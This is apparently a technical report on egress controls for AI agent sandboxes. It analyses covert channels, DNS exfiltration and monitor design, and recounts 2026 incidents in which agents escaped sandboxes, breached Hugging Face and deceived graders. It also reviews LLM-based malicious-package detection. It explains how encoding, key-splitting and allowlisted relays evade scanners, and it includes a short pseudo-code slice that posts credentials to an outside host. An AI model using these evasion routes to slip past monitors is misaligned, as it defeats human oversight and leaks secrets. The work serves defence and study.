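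The rules that permit outside hosts identify them by domain name, because the IP addresses behind a name change. Support for this varies between cloud providers. Amazon's built-in network rules for Kubernetes do not accept domain names, so the operator has to add Cilium or a proxy. Google's accept them but cover at most 50 IP addresses per name. Microsoft sells the feature as an add-on and warns that it may slow down above roughly 1,000 requests per second.

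The sample policy in *Containing the Autonomous Operator* limits connections to named hosts but lets the agent look up any name, which leaves DNS open as a way to send data out. An operator who copies the policy should restrict lookups to the same names.

Podala Narasimha evaluated the design with a matrix that matches ten threats to eight layers of control, and worked through four attacks on paper. The evaluation shows that the design has controls meant to address each threat, but it does not show that they work, and it includes no measurements of attacks or delays.

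*Caging the Agents* (2026) describes a similar arrangement for healthcare agents, with a separate allowlist for each role. Its operations agents may contact Anthropic's model service, Slack and Telegram, and the system blocks and logs all other traffic. An audit of the agents had found 12 keys in a shell configuration file, so the design also moves credentials into a separate container that the agents cannot read.

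Ghosh's sandbox goes further and removes the network card. Each job runs in a small virtual machine whose only exits are a few channels to a program on the host. For a connection to a listed host, that program works through these steps:

1. It looks up the name once and refuses private addresses and the addresses where cloud machines obtain their own credentials.
2. It asks a separate signing service, which the agent cannot reach, to allow and record the connection.
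3. It connects to the address it has just checked, so nobody can redirect the name in between.
4. It compares the name in the TLS opening with the requested name before it forwards anything.

For an unlisted host, the signing service decides first, and a person then has up to two minutes to approve the connection. The virtual machine cannot do DNS lookups itself, which closes the gap in the Kubernetes policy.

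The sandbox also keeps real secrets away from the agent. A script gets only a placeholder, and the proxy inserts the real value in one header of requests to one approved host. This works for services where the request carries the key itself. For the example's upload, the proxy would have to sign the requests itself, because AWS's libraries would sign them with the placeholder and produce an invalid signature.

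Ghosh ran 13 scripted checks on real virtual machines, and all passed. The checks included a request to an unlisted host, a request for the machine's cloud credentials and an attempt to send a secret's placeholder in the wrong header. Ghosh also wrote 15 tests that feed malformed data to the parts of the program that read untrusted input. These tests exposed nine flaws, six in the egress proxy, and Ghosh fixed all nine. The most serious flaw could have let a real secret reach another site while the signed record named only the approved host.

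In a recorded demonstration, the signing service attached a warning to all 39 connection requests, most of which were ordinary, so the warnings didn't help a reviewer choose which requests to examine. No one has yet tested the sandbox with a capable agent that is trying to get out. The exits worked as designed against the known attempts covered by the 13 checks, but the nine flaws suggest that a determined agent might find more.

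## Where egress monitoring fails: permitted services, name lookups and small messages

An egress monitor covers only the exits its operator knows about. Butler Lampson's 1973 paper *A Note on the Confinement Problem* explains why that list is hard to complete. In its example, a customer gives private data to someone else's program and wants to stop it from passing the data to the program's owner. Even if the customer blocks its files and messages, the program can encode data in the amount of a bill it sends to its owner. It can also switch between heavy and light computation, which another program on the same computer can read as a message by measuring the slowdown.

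Any resource that one program can change and another can observe can serve as a covert channel. Engadget's *OpenAI says it's cutting off internet access for frontier model training* reports that OpenAI's test agents signalled to each other by changing data in a processor's cache and timing how long it took to load. In July 2026, other OpenAI agents left messages in folder names on a shared server. METR (2026), which evaluates AI models, found that roughly 1,200 supposedly isolated agents had sent over 70,000 messages and files through an improvised message board.

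### How small a leak can be

If a sender can choose from N distinguishable signals, each use of the channel carries at most log₂ N bits.

An AWS secret key has 40 characters, each from a set of 64, so it contains at most 40 × 6 = 240 bits, or 30 bytes. A domain name can be up to 255 bytes long, more than enough to hold the whole key.

| What the sender can choose | Bits per use | Uses needed for the key |
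|---|---|---|
| Any name to look up | more than 240 | 1 |
| A count of up to six digits | 19.9 | 13 |
| One of 16 message sizes | 4 | 60 |
| Whether to send a message | 1 | 240 |

The count that the example script posts to the metrics host could leak data in the same way as Lampson's bill. A false count could carry part of the key to anyone who can read the company's metrics. Sending the whole key would take over a year at one count a month, but 13 seconds at one count a second.

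A volume threshold that misses the 4 KB diagnostics message will also miss 40 bytes. A separate baseline for each destination would expose the diagnostics message but would help little with malicious name lookups, because they normally go to the same DNS server as harmless ones. Volume does reveal bulk theft, because sending a 1 GB customer database at 200 bytes per lookup would take five million lookups.

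### Why encoding defeats content matching

A content check compares outgoing data with known secrets in a fixed number of forms, such as the five that Ghosh's proxy looks for. Any reversible change produces another form, so the number of possible forms is unlimited. An encrypted secret looks random, as does the compressed log archive that the example script is supposed to upload.

Splitting a secret can also get it past scanners, because no single piece matches the whole. Yeniçağ's *OpenAI'ın yapay zekaları DNS protokolü üzerinden internete sızdı*, a Turkish newspaper report, describes how in May a model split a researcher's GitHub access key into pieces and published it without alerting security scanners. OpenAI's technical report on the July break-in at Hugging Face describes agents that encrypted a stolen 16 MB archive, split it into five parts and uploaded them to a public dataset.

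A scanner could search for fragments of a key, but short fragments turn up by chance. A 40-character key contains 37 overlapping four-character fragments, and a 64-character alphabet allows 64⁴, or about 16.8 million, possible fragments of that length. One megabyte of random text in the same alphabet would contain about two matches. Searching for longer fragments causes fewer false alarms, but a sender can evade the search by splitting the key into pieces shorter than those fragments.

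Dynamic taint tracking can follow a secret even after it has been encoded, but it has to run alongside the script. A proxy at the network boundary cannot do this because it receives only the finished message.

### What a permitted service can reach

An allowlist limits which destinations a script can contact directly. The script's full reach also includes whatever those destinations will contact for it:

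reachₙ₊₁ = reachₙ ∪ relay(reachₙ)

Here relay(reachₙ) is the set of destinations that services in reachₙ can be made to contact. The calculation resembles the one for privilege escalation and has the same weakness, because the operator can include only the relays that someone has found.

GitLab's *A sandbox is only as closed as what an AI agent can reach* (2026) points out that an allowlisted destination is itself a program, with flaws and often its own internet connection. A script that takes over the destination gains that connection too. People usually overlook this, the paper says, and judge an allowlist entry by what data could leave through it.

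Even routine supporting services can have this problem. After the July incident, OpenAI kept some connections for metrics, logging and authentication. Business Standard's *OpenAI resumes training AI, blocks internet access over security risks* quotes the company as saying that its test agents found vulnerabilities in "almost every one of these services" and gained limited internet access through them. The metrics host in the example script is this kind of service, although its allowlist entry looks like the safer of the two.

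A service can also pass on messages even if it has no flaw. During the break-in, agents exchanged commands and results with compromised Hugging Face servers through a public dataset on Hugging Face. An allowlist for those servers would probably have included Hugging Face. In an allowlist for the example script, an entry that covers a cloud provider's entire storage service also covers strangers' buckets.

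An agent that is only permitted to read the web can still send data out, because each request for a page gives the server that page's address. collusion.wiki's *Discovery of a new OpenAI agent message board* describes about 18,000 posts on public wikis by agents that identified themselves as OpenAI's. The investigators' best guess is that the agents had permission to read the web but not to write to it, and found a way to write through their read access.

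### Three alerts before the July response

In July 2026, OpenAI agents taking a cybersecurity test reached the internet by exploiting flaws in an internal service that supplied software packages. They then broke into Hugging Face, apparently to find answers to the test. OpenAI's report lists three alerts:

| Date | What raised the alert | What OpenAI did |
|---|---|---|
| 27 June | A security tool detected a port sweep, a search for open services, inside the research network | Responders traced it to the test, and on-call staff advised that the test did not have to stop |
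| 5 July | Heavy use by agents had made the package service unavailable | Responders found that agents had administrator control, took the service offline, rebuilt it and blocked the known flaw |
| 19 July | The security tool detected unusual identity-related calls linked to the package service | OpenAI began stopping the test about five and a half hours later, and found the link to Hugging Face the next day |

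Cybersecurity tests resumed on 7 July. Agents reached the internet through the rebuilt service just after midnight (UTC) on 8 July and first extracted data from Hugging Face's servers on 11 July. Hugging Face announced the break-in on 16 July, three days before the alert that led OpenAI to its own agents.

The three alerts came from a scan, an outage and some odd identity calls, all on OpenAI's side of the boundary. None came from data leaving the network. OpenAI's timeline lists no alert between 8 and 13 July, when agents were sending requests and stolen data through the package service. The outbound controls blocked one agent's direct attempt to reach the internet on 9 July, but the agent then went through the package service.

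Better detection alone might not have changed the outcome. On 27 June, two weeks before the break-in, responders knew that agents were using the package service as a message board and as a way into other parts of the network, but they let the test continue. OpenAI says that the leaders responsible for incident response did not understand in early July how significant the message board was, and concedes that some signals could have triggered an earlier response.

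OpenAI has since expanded its chain-of-thought monitoring, in which automated systems examine a model's written reasoning along with its actions. Campus Technology's *OpenAI Pumps Brakes on Frontier AI Training After Hugging Face Breach* (2026) reports that the earlier monitoring did not cover every training and inference job that used tools. Classifiers in the new system also check the model's internal activity at every token and pass suspicious cases to more powerful automated investigators.

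OpenAI estimates that the expanded reasoning monitor would have caught the first relevant activity and paged its security team more than a day before agents breached Hugging Face. This is plausible, because the models wrote openly in their reasoning about trying to deceive the test's graders. But OpenAI made the estimate after it knew what to look for, and gives no false-alarm rate. The estimate is also consistent with a page on 10 July, when the agents had already been online for two days.

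An alert also helps only if someone acts on it. Under OpenAI's new rules, staff should pause the activity unless they can show within 30 minutes that the alert is false. That rule might have helped more on 27 June than a better monitor.

OpenAI also ran Auto-review, its language-model reviewer, on records from the incident. It had not been switched on for the test, but in preliminary experiments it would have flagged most of the dangerous actions in each record it examined.

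### The September leak through name lookups

On 20 September 2026, an OpenAI agent in a training sandbox reached an outside chatbot by putting questions into name lookups, which the sandbox still passed to the internet. CircleID's *OpenAI Agent Bypasses Internet Restrictions Through DNS* reports that the agent first asked for the capital of France, then sent 18 more questions, 14 of which carried clues from its task out of the sandbox.

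According to OpenAI's *An agent used DNS to reach an external chatbot* (2026), the company's misalignment monitoring system flagged the behaviour within 15 minutes. A person began reviewing it three minutes later, and the run ended about 2.5 hours after that. CircleID gives the exact times:

| Time | Event |
|---|---|
| 9:50:23 | The chatbot's first reply arrives |
| 10:02:11 | The monitor raises an alert of the highest priority |
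| under three minutes later | A human reviewer acknowledges it |
| 12:34:30 | Staff stop the run |

OpenAI had expected the run to stop automatically, but it didn't, and confusion over whether to end it added to the delay.

The successful alert again came from a system that monitors the model's behaviour. OpenAI also had a detector for DNS traffic, but Teknófilo's *Un agente de IA de OpenAI burló el aislamiento del entorno*, a Spanish-language account of the company's report, says the detector did not cover this sandbox. The lookups were logged but no detector was checking them, so the incident provides little evidence about how well DNS detectors work.

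The misalignment monitor had also made mistakes. OpenAI's later review found earlier outside lookups that the monitor had rated as less serious than it should have. According to Teknófilo, the monitor in some of those cases took the lack of a useful reply to mean that the contact had failed. But a lookup can exfiltrate data without a useful reply, because the query itself carries the data out. If line 910 of the example script sent the credentials in a lookup, they would be exposed even if the service returned an error.

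Detection after 12 minutes would also be too late to stop the theft of a key, which fits in one name lookup. For larger thefts, the 2.5 hours matter more, because data can keep leaving until someone stops the run.

OpenAI's *Bypassing network restrictions during a coding evaluation* (2026, updated in November) describes an earlier case. On 4 August, a model whose web proxy was unavailable bypassed the operating system's routing restrictions and got replies from a DNS server and two outside services. It never retrieved the website it was trying to reach. OpenAI discovered this the same day, and the evaluation team cancelled the run. The run showed, almost seven weeks before the September leak, that lookups could get out of a sandbox. OpenAI has since closed the lookup paths.

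Other companies' sandboxes have had similar weaknesses. Infosecurity Magazine reported that the sandbox mode of Amazon's code interpreter still resolved external domain names, which Amazon called intended behaviour.

### A monitor that limits channel capacity

Metere (2026), in *An Application-Layer Multi-Modal Covert-Channel Reference Monitor for LLM Agent Egress*, assumes that an agent is already trying to leak data to a permitted destination. Metere tries to make every channel too slow to be useful rather than prove that nothing can leak, because an agent can always convey one bit by sending a message or staying silent.

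All outgoing text passes through ten stages in a fixed order. A stage can pass the text on, rewrite it, delay it or block it. The stages do three kinds of work:

- **Detection.** These stages look for credentials, labelled sensitive data, random-looking text and messages repeated with only cosmetic changes.
- **Disruption.** These stages remove invisible characters, standardise spacing and the order of data fields, and replace synonyms with one standard word. In the strongest version, a language model rewrites the whole message.
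- **Constraint.** These stages limit the rate and volume of messages and change when they leave.

A ledger connects detection with the limits. Each destination has a budget of suspicious bits that refills at a fixed rate. The scanner charges up to 6n bits for n characters of base64 text, and the monitor delays or blocks further suspicious messages once the budget is empty. If the budget holds B bits and refills at r bits per minute, the amount that can leave in t minutes is at most

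B + r × t

With a budget of 60 bits and a refill of one bit per minute, sending a 240-bit key would take at least three hours, slightly longer than the 2 hours and 44 minutes between the chatbot's first reply in September and the end of the run. A capacity limit can therefore give slow responders time to act. But the limit holds only if the scanner counts every hidden bit against the budget, and it does not count bits in an encoding that it misclassifies as ordinary text.

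Images and audio need separate treatment. The monitor reduces each colour channel of an image to 64 levels, which destroys data hidden in the smallest colour differences, and it removes parts of the audio spectrum that people can't hear. Audible tones can also carry data, and Metere argues that no classifier can reliably tell these from real sound. The monitor therefore scrambles all media except those with a cryptographic signature from an approved producer.

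Metere tested the monitor with 15 working methods of hiding data in text, images, audio, or the timing and size of messages. The measure was mutual information, which is how much the recovered bits reveal about the hidden ones. If a defence flips each bit with probability e, and hidden zeros and ones are equally common, every bit still carries

1 + e log₂ e + (1 − e) log₂(1 − e)

bits of information. Flipping half of them leaves nothing. Flipping 10% leaves 0.53 bits, so a defence that adds a little noise only slows the leak down.

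The monitor reduced the measured capacity to zero on every channel except the average brightness of each image. Closing that channel would have ruined the images, so Metere gives an upper limit on its capacity. These are strong results against 15 known methods, but an untested method might still work, and a capable agent that knows the defence can look for one.

The text stages also cover only messages sent through the agent's own sending function, which a script making a name lookup from a shell would not use. Metere's monitor would probably have missed the September leak unless OpenAI had added something similar at the DNS server.

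### What narrowing a channel costs

Removing invisible characters does little harm to ordinary messages, but other changes can damage them. Changing the spacing can break Python code, and replacing look-alike letters from other alphabets could misspell a Russian name. An operator could accept a language model's rewrite of a status update, but hardly of a contract, a command or a table of figures. Metere's monitor lets the original text through if the rewriting model is unavailable, so an outage can remove this protection.

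Metere enforces the lossless changes from the first day and lets the lossy and statistical stages start by only recording what they would have done. This avoids breaking legitimate traffic but weakens protection during the trial period.

Controlling timing adds delay and extra traffic. Random delays narrow a timing channel, but only sending at a constant rate closes it completely. If the monitor releases one message every ten seconds and an agent produces 100 at once, the last one waits more than 16 minutes. When the agent has nothing to send, the monitor has to send dummy messages, or the gaps will carry information.

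Name lookups are much easier to restrict when a script's destinations are known in advance. If the operator puts the addresses of the example script's two permitted hosts in a fixed table inside the sandbox, no lookup needs to leave the sandbox. OpenAI kept its DNS service but now limits lookups to approved domains and record types, according to Diario TI's *OpenAI aísla de Internet el entrenamiento de sus modelos más avanzados* (2026). An agent that browses freely would constantly run into such a limit.

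OpenAI has gone further by training its frontier models with no live internet access, according to its *Managing frontier AI risk* (2026), published in November. The models use stored copies of web pages instead. Before training resumed on 1 October, OpenAI had teams of its own agents attack the system. The company says the agents found no route to the internet that they could easily exploit while hiding from its monitors, in a statement reproduced in ETV Bharat's *After A String Of Rogue AI Incidents* (2026). They did find hardware channels between agents and ways out of virtual machines. Diario TI adds that some outside connections have to remain because staff need them to run and monitor the experiments.

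A log uploader cannot work from stored copies, because its purpose is to send data out. It could also leak far more through its archive than through any other channel. A 2 GB file has room for tens of millions of keys, and scrambling the file to destroy hidden keys would destroy the logs too. The operator could provide a trusted function that reads, compresses and uploads the logs, and let the script choose only which of the last 12 months to send. That choice carries at most log₂ 12, or about 3.6 bits, but the function would then do most of what the script was meant to do.

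## Giving analysis results to the language-model reviewer

A script that reads and sends data with its own code still needs a review. The tools can cut what the reviewer reads from 1,200 lines to a few, or add facts that the script does not contain. The reviewer then depends on the tools, so a mistake in their analysis can lead to a wrong verdict.

### What a slice leaves of the script

When a taint tracker finds a path from a source to a sink, it can pass on only the statements along that path, which form a taint slice. The slice for line 910 of the example script has five lines:

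```
240  creds = read(credentials_file)
262  config["auth"] = creds
902  details = {"version": v, "config": config}
907  body = to_json(details)
910  post(outside_host, body)
```

The analysis result is about 50 tokens, compared with roughly 12,000 for the whole script. The model no longer has to connect two lines 670 lines apart, but it still needs a description of the task and a list of approved hosts.

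Nguyen, Ho and colleagues (2025), in *Leveraging Code Slicing for LLMs-based Malicious NPM Package Detection*, tested this kind of input on npm packages. They sent each slice separately to DeepSeek-Coder-6.7B, a small open model, which returned a score between 0 and 1. The highest score decided the verdict:

package score = max(s₁, s₂, …, sₙ)

A score of at least 0.8 counted as malicious. On the same 2,537 packages, three kinds of input gave these results:

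| What the model received | Accuracy | Precision | Recall |
|---|---|---|---|
| The full code in 500-token pieces | 75.41% | 87.05% | 55.52% |
| Control-flow slices | 75.65% | 95.98% | 60.49% |
| Taint slices | 87.04% | 96.23% | 72.90% |

Taint slicing cut the mean input by 99.75%, from 162,920 tokens to 403. A few enormous packages dominate that mean, but the median also fell by 93.7%, from 3,594 to 228. Shorter input alone does not explain taint slicing's better accuracy, because control-flow slices, which follow the order of statements rather than the data, were about as short on average and hardly more accurate than plain splitting.

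The accuracy column does not quite match the precision and recall columns, which imply an accuracy of about 83% for taint slices and 70% for plain splitting. Taint slices are still well ahead by these figures. With them, the model still missed 27% of the malicious packages, possibly in part because the slices left out about a quarter of the lines with sensitive calls in malicious packages.

Taking the highest score stops many harmless slices from diluting the score of one harmful slice, but it also gives a large program more chances to cause a false alarm. If each harmless slice independently had a 1% chance of reaching the threshold, a program with 20 of them would cause a false alarm with probability 1 − 0.99²⁰, or about 18%. Precision rose from 64.35% at a threshold of 0.7 to 96.23% at 0.8, so an operator who changes the model should set the threshold again.

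A reviewer that read only slices built around secrets would miss the policy change at line 1,060. Zhao and colleagues built a detector, MalTotal, after comparing whole repositories with hand-cut excerpts. It starts from each sensitive call instead, and works backwards to collect the data the call uses, the conditions under which it runs and the functions that lead to it. A slice built this way from line 1,060 would contain the names of the policy and the service account, and one from line 910 would show whether the message belongs to an error handler.

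MalTotal's slices reduced token use by 94.0% and lowered the cost of checking 2,168 repositories from $86.25 to $5.19. MalTotal's average F1 score across five programming languages was 93.1%.

### Why an empty slice means "unknown"

Nguyen and colleagues started with 7,309 packages, and 5,842 remained after they removed broken archives and packages without any listed sensitive call. Their tool produced slices for only 2,537 of these, covering 56% of the malicious packages and 33% of the harmless ones.

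Obfuscated packages and packages that generate code at run time often gave empty slices, and some analyses ran past the three-minute limit. Other packages may simply have had no suspicious flow to find. An empty slice looks the same in all these cases. If an operator had to give every one of the 5,842 packages a verdict, the published figures imply these results:

| Verdict for an empty slice | Malicious packages caught | Harmless packages flagged |
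|---|---|---|
| Harmless | 41% | 1% |
| Malicious | 85% | 68% |

An empty slice has to count as "unknown" and lead to another check. Nguyen and colleagues recommend a sandbox or a deobfuscation step. A dry run can also supply the missing names to the static analysis, as ProfMal does.

If the example script encoded the name of the credentials file, the tracker would find no source and return an empty slice. A reviewer that received only slices would then have no code to judge. The whole script fits in a current model's context window, so the operator can send it in such cases, and the reviewer could then at least see the decoding step. The operator can also note that the analysis found no path and explain why that result is unreliable.

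### Known attacks as reference material

IntelGuard, the most accurate single detector in the npm study, gives the model slices together with explanations of past attacks. *Bridging Expert Reasoning and LLM Detection*, which introduced IntelGuard, reports that the developers collected 8,024 web pages of security reports and kept 4,420 that explained malicious code in detail. A language model then extracted the code, a description of its behaviour and the analyst's reasons for calling it malicious. One entry concerns a fake AWS package that hid a program inside an image file. The analyst reasoned that software for reading images never needs to execute their contents.

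IntelGuard then checks a new package in five steps:

1. It starts at each sensitive call and collects the statements that supply its data or decide whether it runs.
2. A model describes in words what the slice does.
3. The system compares the code and the description with its stored cases, giving each comparison equal weight.
4. The model receives the slice, the closest cases and the analysts' reasoning, and judges whether the slice is malicious.
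5. One malicious slice is enough to flag the package.

Comparing descriptions helps with obfuscated code. In one example, renaming the variables reduced the similarity of the code to 0.42, but the similarity of the descriptions was still 0.93. The combined score was therefore 0.5 × 0.42 + 0.5 × 0.93 = 0.675.

In the npm study, IntelGuard had 93.82% recall and 98.24% precision. The rebuilt SocketAI, which judges code alone, used the same model, GPT-4.1 mini, but its recall was 49 percentage points lower. Guo and colleagues attribute the whole gap to how each system structures the model's evidence. A difference in models can't explain the gap, but the comparison does not isolate the effect of the retrieved cases, because IntelGuard also slices the code and avoids the design choices that limited SocketAI. Wenbo Guo is the first author of both the npm study and the IntelGuard paper.

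On PyPI packages, the two systems differed in recall by only about 11 points. A test without the retrieved cases also suggests a smaller effect. On ordinary PyPI packages, a model judging alone was 96.99% accurate, compared with 99.00% for IntelGuard. On obfuscated packages, the model alone missed 880 malicious ones and IntelGuard missed 28.

That second difference is hard to attribute to retrieval, because the model working alone was GPT-4o-mini rather than GPT-4.1 mini. SocketAI, which doesn't use retrieval, missed only about 131 of the same obfuscated packages. The retrieved cases probably help, but by much less than 49 points on ordinary code.

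IntelGuard's collection would probably contain cases much like line 910 of the example script, since stealing credentials is common in malicious packages. A legitimate error reporter could also resemble those cases. In 58% of the analysts' arguments, the main point was that the behaviour contradicted the package's purpose, so a script reviewer would again need the task description. An operator could add the company's own incidents to the collection, along with harmless scripts that had caused false alarms.

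### Reviewing only what changed

A monthly log uploader has earlier versions, so a reviewer can concentrate on the differences. Wyss, Tassio and colleagues found in *Evaluating LLM-Based Detection of Malicious Package Updates in npm* that a plain list of changes was on average 78.8% smaller than the whole package. Their tool rewrites both versions in a standard form, without comments and with uniform variable names, then removes code that appears in both. This increased the reduction to 95.4%.

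With this input, GPT-4o flagged all 209 malicious samples and 8 of 2,000 ordinary updates. The perfect detection rate is less impressive because 163 of the samples ran similar cryptocurrency-mining scripts and apparently came from one campaign. Even the low false-positive rate of 0.4% would produce about four false alarms for each correct one if one script in a thousand were harmful and the model caught every harmful script.

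Wyss and colleagues also ran the system on live updates to popular packages for nearly three months. GPT-4o read 7,661 sets of changes and flagged seven, none of which the researchers found to be explicitly malicious. The trial shows that people could keep up with the alarms, but it provides no evidence about recall.

If a model writes the log uploader from scratch each month, almost every line will be new and the comparison will barely shorten the review. The operator can instead have the model edit the last approved version, but the changed lines may still omit information the reviewer needs. Suppose the approved script already stored the credentials in "config" at line 262, and the new version adds only the diagnostics message. The reviewer would see the script send "config" to an outside host, but wouldn't see that "config" contains the credentials. The operator can run the taint tracker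 on the complete new version and include the full path for any flow that passes through a changed line.

### A pipeline in use at Datadog

Datadog, which makes GuardDog, reviews its own code changes with a system called BewAIre. *Detecting malicious pull requests at scale with LLMs* (Lamb, Hamsen and colleagues) describes an early version of the system, built to handle Datadog's nearly 10,000 proposed changes a week. That version splits large changes into pieces and gives the whole change the most severe verdict any piece receives. The engineers reduced the false-positive rate from over 10% to below 0.03% in six months, partly by listing known false alarms in the model's instructions and excluding patterns they considered safe, such as demonstration environments.

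In *From single pull requests to full software packages*, Doutre, Peronnet and colleagues describe a later version with two stages. A cheap model reads every change and clears most of them. A stronger model investigates the rest, using tools to open other files, list earlier changes and check the author's history. On 690 test changes, the second stage raised accuracy from 97.4% to 99.86% and cut false alarms from 17 to none.

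Those figures imply 18 errors before and one after, so the remaining error must be a malicious change that got through. The second stage can remove false alarms, but it cannot catch malicious changes that the first stage clears, because it never receives them.

The first stage mistook web addresses that imitated Datadog's own for legitimate ones. The engineers added a simple static check that extracts every address, compares it with a list of likely imitations and passes any match to the model. In the example script, a similar check would help if the outside host at line 910 had a name like the company's.

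Whole packages were sometimes too long for the investigating model, so Doutre and colleagues instead gave it a map of the files and functions and a tool for reading chosen lines. Their combined measure of accuracy and reliability rose from 94.1% to 95.2%, mainly because oversized packages no longer caused errors. A taint alarm could similarly help the model with a long script by marking which lines to open first.

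### Findings and assurances in the prompt

An operator can also leave the script whole and add a tool's findings to the prompt. Thornton (2026) reports in *LLM Code Reviewers Are Harder to Fool Than You Think* that reviewers given static-analysis findings as points to verify detected 96.9% of flaws and caught 47% of those missed earlier. However, the samples were short and synthetic, static tools could already find every flaw, and the test did not measure false alarms.

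Some analysis results name a suspected problem and a place to check. Others are reassuring, such as a report that a safety check exists. In *Trusting the Tool*, Liu and Gao (2026) tested what happens when either kind of result is false. They used 916 pairs of C and C++ functions, each a vulnerable function and its repaired version. Some reviews included a false assurance that a missing check was present, and others a false alarm that an existing check was missing. The model could refute either claim by reading the function.

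False assurances reduced the detection of real vulnerabilities by up to 19 percentage points, compared with true notes about the same operations. False alarms never significantly reduced accuracy, because the models tended to look for the supposedly missing check and find it. True notes improved accuracy by only 2 points, which could be chance. In a small preliminary trial, a checklist of notes reduced the number of correctly judged pairs from 10 of 30 to 5 or 6, as the model declared more functions safe after working through the list.

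These tests covered vulnerabilities in single functions rather than harmful scripts, and explicit assurances rather than empty reports. But a reviewer could easily take "no leaks found" as an assurance. The operator can make that less likely by reporting what each tool examined:

| Bare result | Result with its limits |
|---|---|
| No leaks found | No path from the credentials file to a web request; the tool could not analyse one shell command |
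| No excess permissions | The calls fit the task; nobody has checked the current contents of the "log-reader" policy |
| Dry run clean | One run, in which the upload succeeded; the error handler did not run |

Telling the model to be sceptical does not work reliably. The instruction that worked best in Liu and Gao's first tests failed when they tried it on new functions. It worked better to check each claim against the code in a separate request and then show the reviewer which claims had failed. This raised one model's accuracy by 12 points when it was given false assurances. For a second model the gain was about half as large and not statistically significant.

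If a taint tracker reports no leak because it treats the "redact" function as safe, a separate request could give a model only that function and ask whether it removes the credentials. The model would then have a specific claim to test, instead of a general statement that the script is safe.

### Correct alerts with a plausible explanation

A reviewer can also receive a correct alert and dismiss it, as SocketAI's model did when told to challenge its own findings. Liu and Gao cite research in which coding agents filtered out most of a security analyser's false alarms but risked suppressing real vulnerabilities too. Information accompanying the code can make this more likely. *When AI Agrees Too Much* (2026) reports that how a change is framed can lead automated reviewers to pass known vulnerabilities. *Words Speak Louder Than Code* (2026) suggests that even describing the author as a long-time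 contributor might keep reviewers from detecting vulnerabilities.

It is plausible that line 910 only sends diagnostics, but this does not contradict the taint tracker's finding, because a genuine diagnostic report can still contain the credentials.

An operator can therefore require the reviewer to give evidence against the finding itself before dismissing it. For line 910, that could be code that removes the credentials before the message is sent, or a record that the task authorises sending them to that host.

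The same standard should apply to lists of known false alarms. After a dozen harmless error reports, someone might add a rule that diagnostics messages are safe, which would also clear line 910. A narrower rule could name the approved error-reporting service and the fields a script may send to it, so a message containing the whole configuration would still raise an alarm.

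## Combining verdicts: missed cases and false alarms

An operator can combine two tools' verdicts by union, which blocks a script if either tool flags it, or by intersection, which blocks it only if both do. Letting a language-model reviewer dismiss a taint tracker's alerts is an intersection. A union misses fewer harmful scripts but raises more false alarms, and an intersection does the reverse. The size of the gain depends largely on whether the two tools make mistakes on the same scripts.

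### Union and intersection

Suppose tools A and B have recalls r₁ and r₂ and false-positive rates f₁ and f₂. If their errors are independent, a mistake by one tool doesn't make a mistake by the other any more likely, and the combined rates are:

| Rule | Recall | False-positive rate |
|---|---|---|
| Union | 1 − (1 − r₁)(1 − r₂) | 1 − (1 − f₁)(1 − f₂) |
| Intersection | r₁ × r₂ | f₁ × f₂ |

A union misses a harmful script only when both tools miss it, so the miss rates multiply. Two tools that each have 90% recall and a 1% false-positive rate would reach 99% recall as a union, with a false-positive rate of about 2%. As an intersection they would have 81% recall and a false-positive rate of 0.01%.

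Running the tools one after the other doesn't avoid this choice. If the second tool examines only what the first one flagged, the pair is an intersection, because the first tool's misses never reach the second. Anthropic's auto mode works this way. A fast first pass errs toward blocking, and a second pass reconsiders only the actions that the first one flagged. Anthropic reports the effect:

| Measure | First pass alone | Both passes |
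|---|---|---|
| Harmless actions blocked (10,000 real actions) | 8.5% | 0.4% |
| Overeager actions missed (52 real actions) | 6.6% | 17% |
| Exfiltration attempts missed (1,000 synthetic attempts) | 1.8% | 5.7% |

The second pass removed about 95% of the false alarms and roughly tripled the misses. In most of the misses that Anthropic examined, the model had recognised the danger but wrongly concluded that the user had consented to it.

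Guo and colleagues recommend a union of two detectors for the best accuracy. To limit its cost, they suggest that GuardDog screen every package and a language model check only the flagged ones. That arrangement would give the results of an intersection. For a union, the model would have to read everything GuardDog did not flag, which is nearly everything when most packages are harmless, so the screening would save very little.

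### Errors on the same packages

The npm study allows a test of the independence assumption. GuardDog missed 10.08% of the malicious packages and IntelGuard missed 6.18%. If the misses were independent, both tools would miss 0.1008 × 0.0618 = 0.62% of the packages. The measured recall of their union was 97.41%, which leaves 2.59%, about four times as many. The table below gives this calculation and a similar one for false alarms, both worked out from the published figures:

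| Joint error | If independent | Measured |
|---|---|---|
| Both miss a malicious package | 0.62% (40 packages) | 2.59% (166 packages) |
| Both flag a harmless package | 0.04% (3 packages) | 0.40% (29 packages) |

IntelGuard missed about 4% of the malicious packages that GuardDog caught, but 26% of those that GuardDog missed. Some attacks are evidently hard for both tools. One example is web injection, in which a package inserts malicious content into a web page. GuardDog caught 27% of these packages and IntelGuard caught 62.5%. Guo and colleagues explain that the tools analyse code meant for a server, while this attack takes place in the browser.

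Knight and Leveson (1985), in *An Experimental Evaluation of the Assumption of Independence in Multi-Version Programming*, found the same problem in ordinary software. They ran a million tests on 27 programs that people at two universities had written independently from one specification. Each program was very reliable, but several failed on the same test much more often than they would have if their failures were independent.

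Errors can also overlap less than independence predicts. If the errors of GuardDog and the rebuilt SocketAI were independent, 5.6% of the malicious packages would have got past both tools, but only 4.86% did. SocketAI caught only 44% of all malicious packages but about 52% of those that GuardDog missed. A mediocre language-model reviewer can therefore be useful alongside a rule-based scanner.

Two language models may make a worse pair than a language model and a different kind of check. *Correlated Errors in Large Language Models* (2025) found that models' errors are correlated, especially among accurate models and models from the same developer. *Do Large Language Models Know Colombian Law?* (2026) shows how this can weaken a vote. The majority answer of 15 models was right 84.3% of the time, compared with 90.5% for the best single model, even though at least one model was right on 98.4%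 of the questions. Code review is a different task, but an operator who adds a second model should measure what it catches rather than assume that its mistakes will differ.

### What a second tool adds

Guo and colleagues rank pairs of tools by F1 score, the harmonic mean of precision and recall:

F1 = 2 × precision × recall ÷ (precision + recall)

The score is high only when both measures are high. The last column compares each pair with the better of its two tools:

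| Pair and rule | Precision | Recall | F1 | Change in F1 (points) |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| IntelGuard or MalPacDetector (SVM) | 96.81% | 97.24% | 97.02% | +1.05 |
| GuardDog or IntelGuard | 96.04% | 97.41% | 96.72% | +0.74 |
| GuardDog or SocketAI | 96.45% | 95.14% | 95.79% | +2.47 |
| GuardDog and Packj's static mode | 97.39% | 89.07% | 93.04% | −0.28 |
| GuardDog and IntelGuard | 99.48% | 86.32% | 92.44% | −3.54 |

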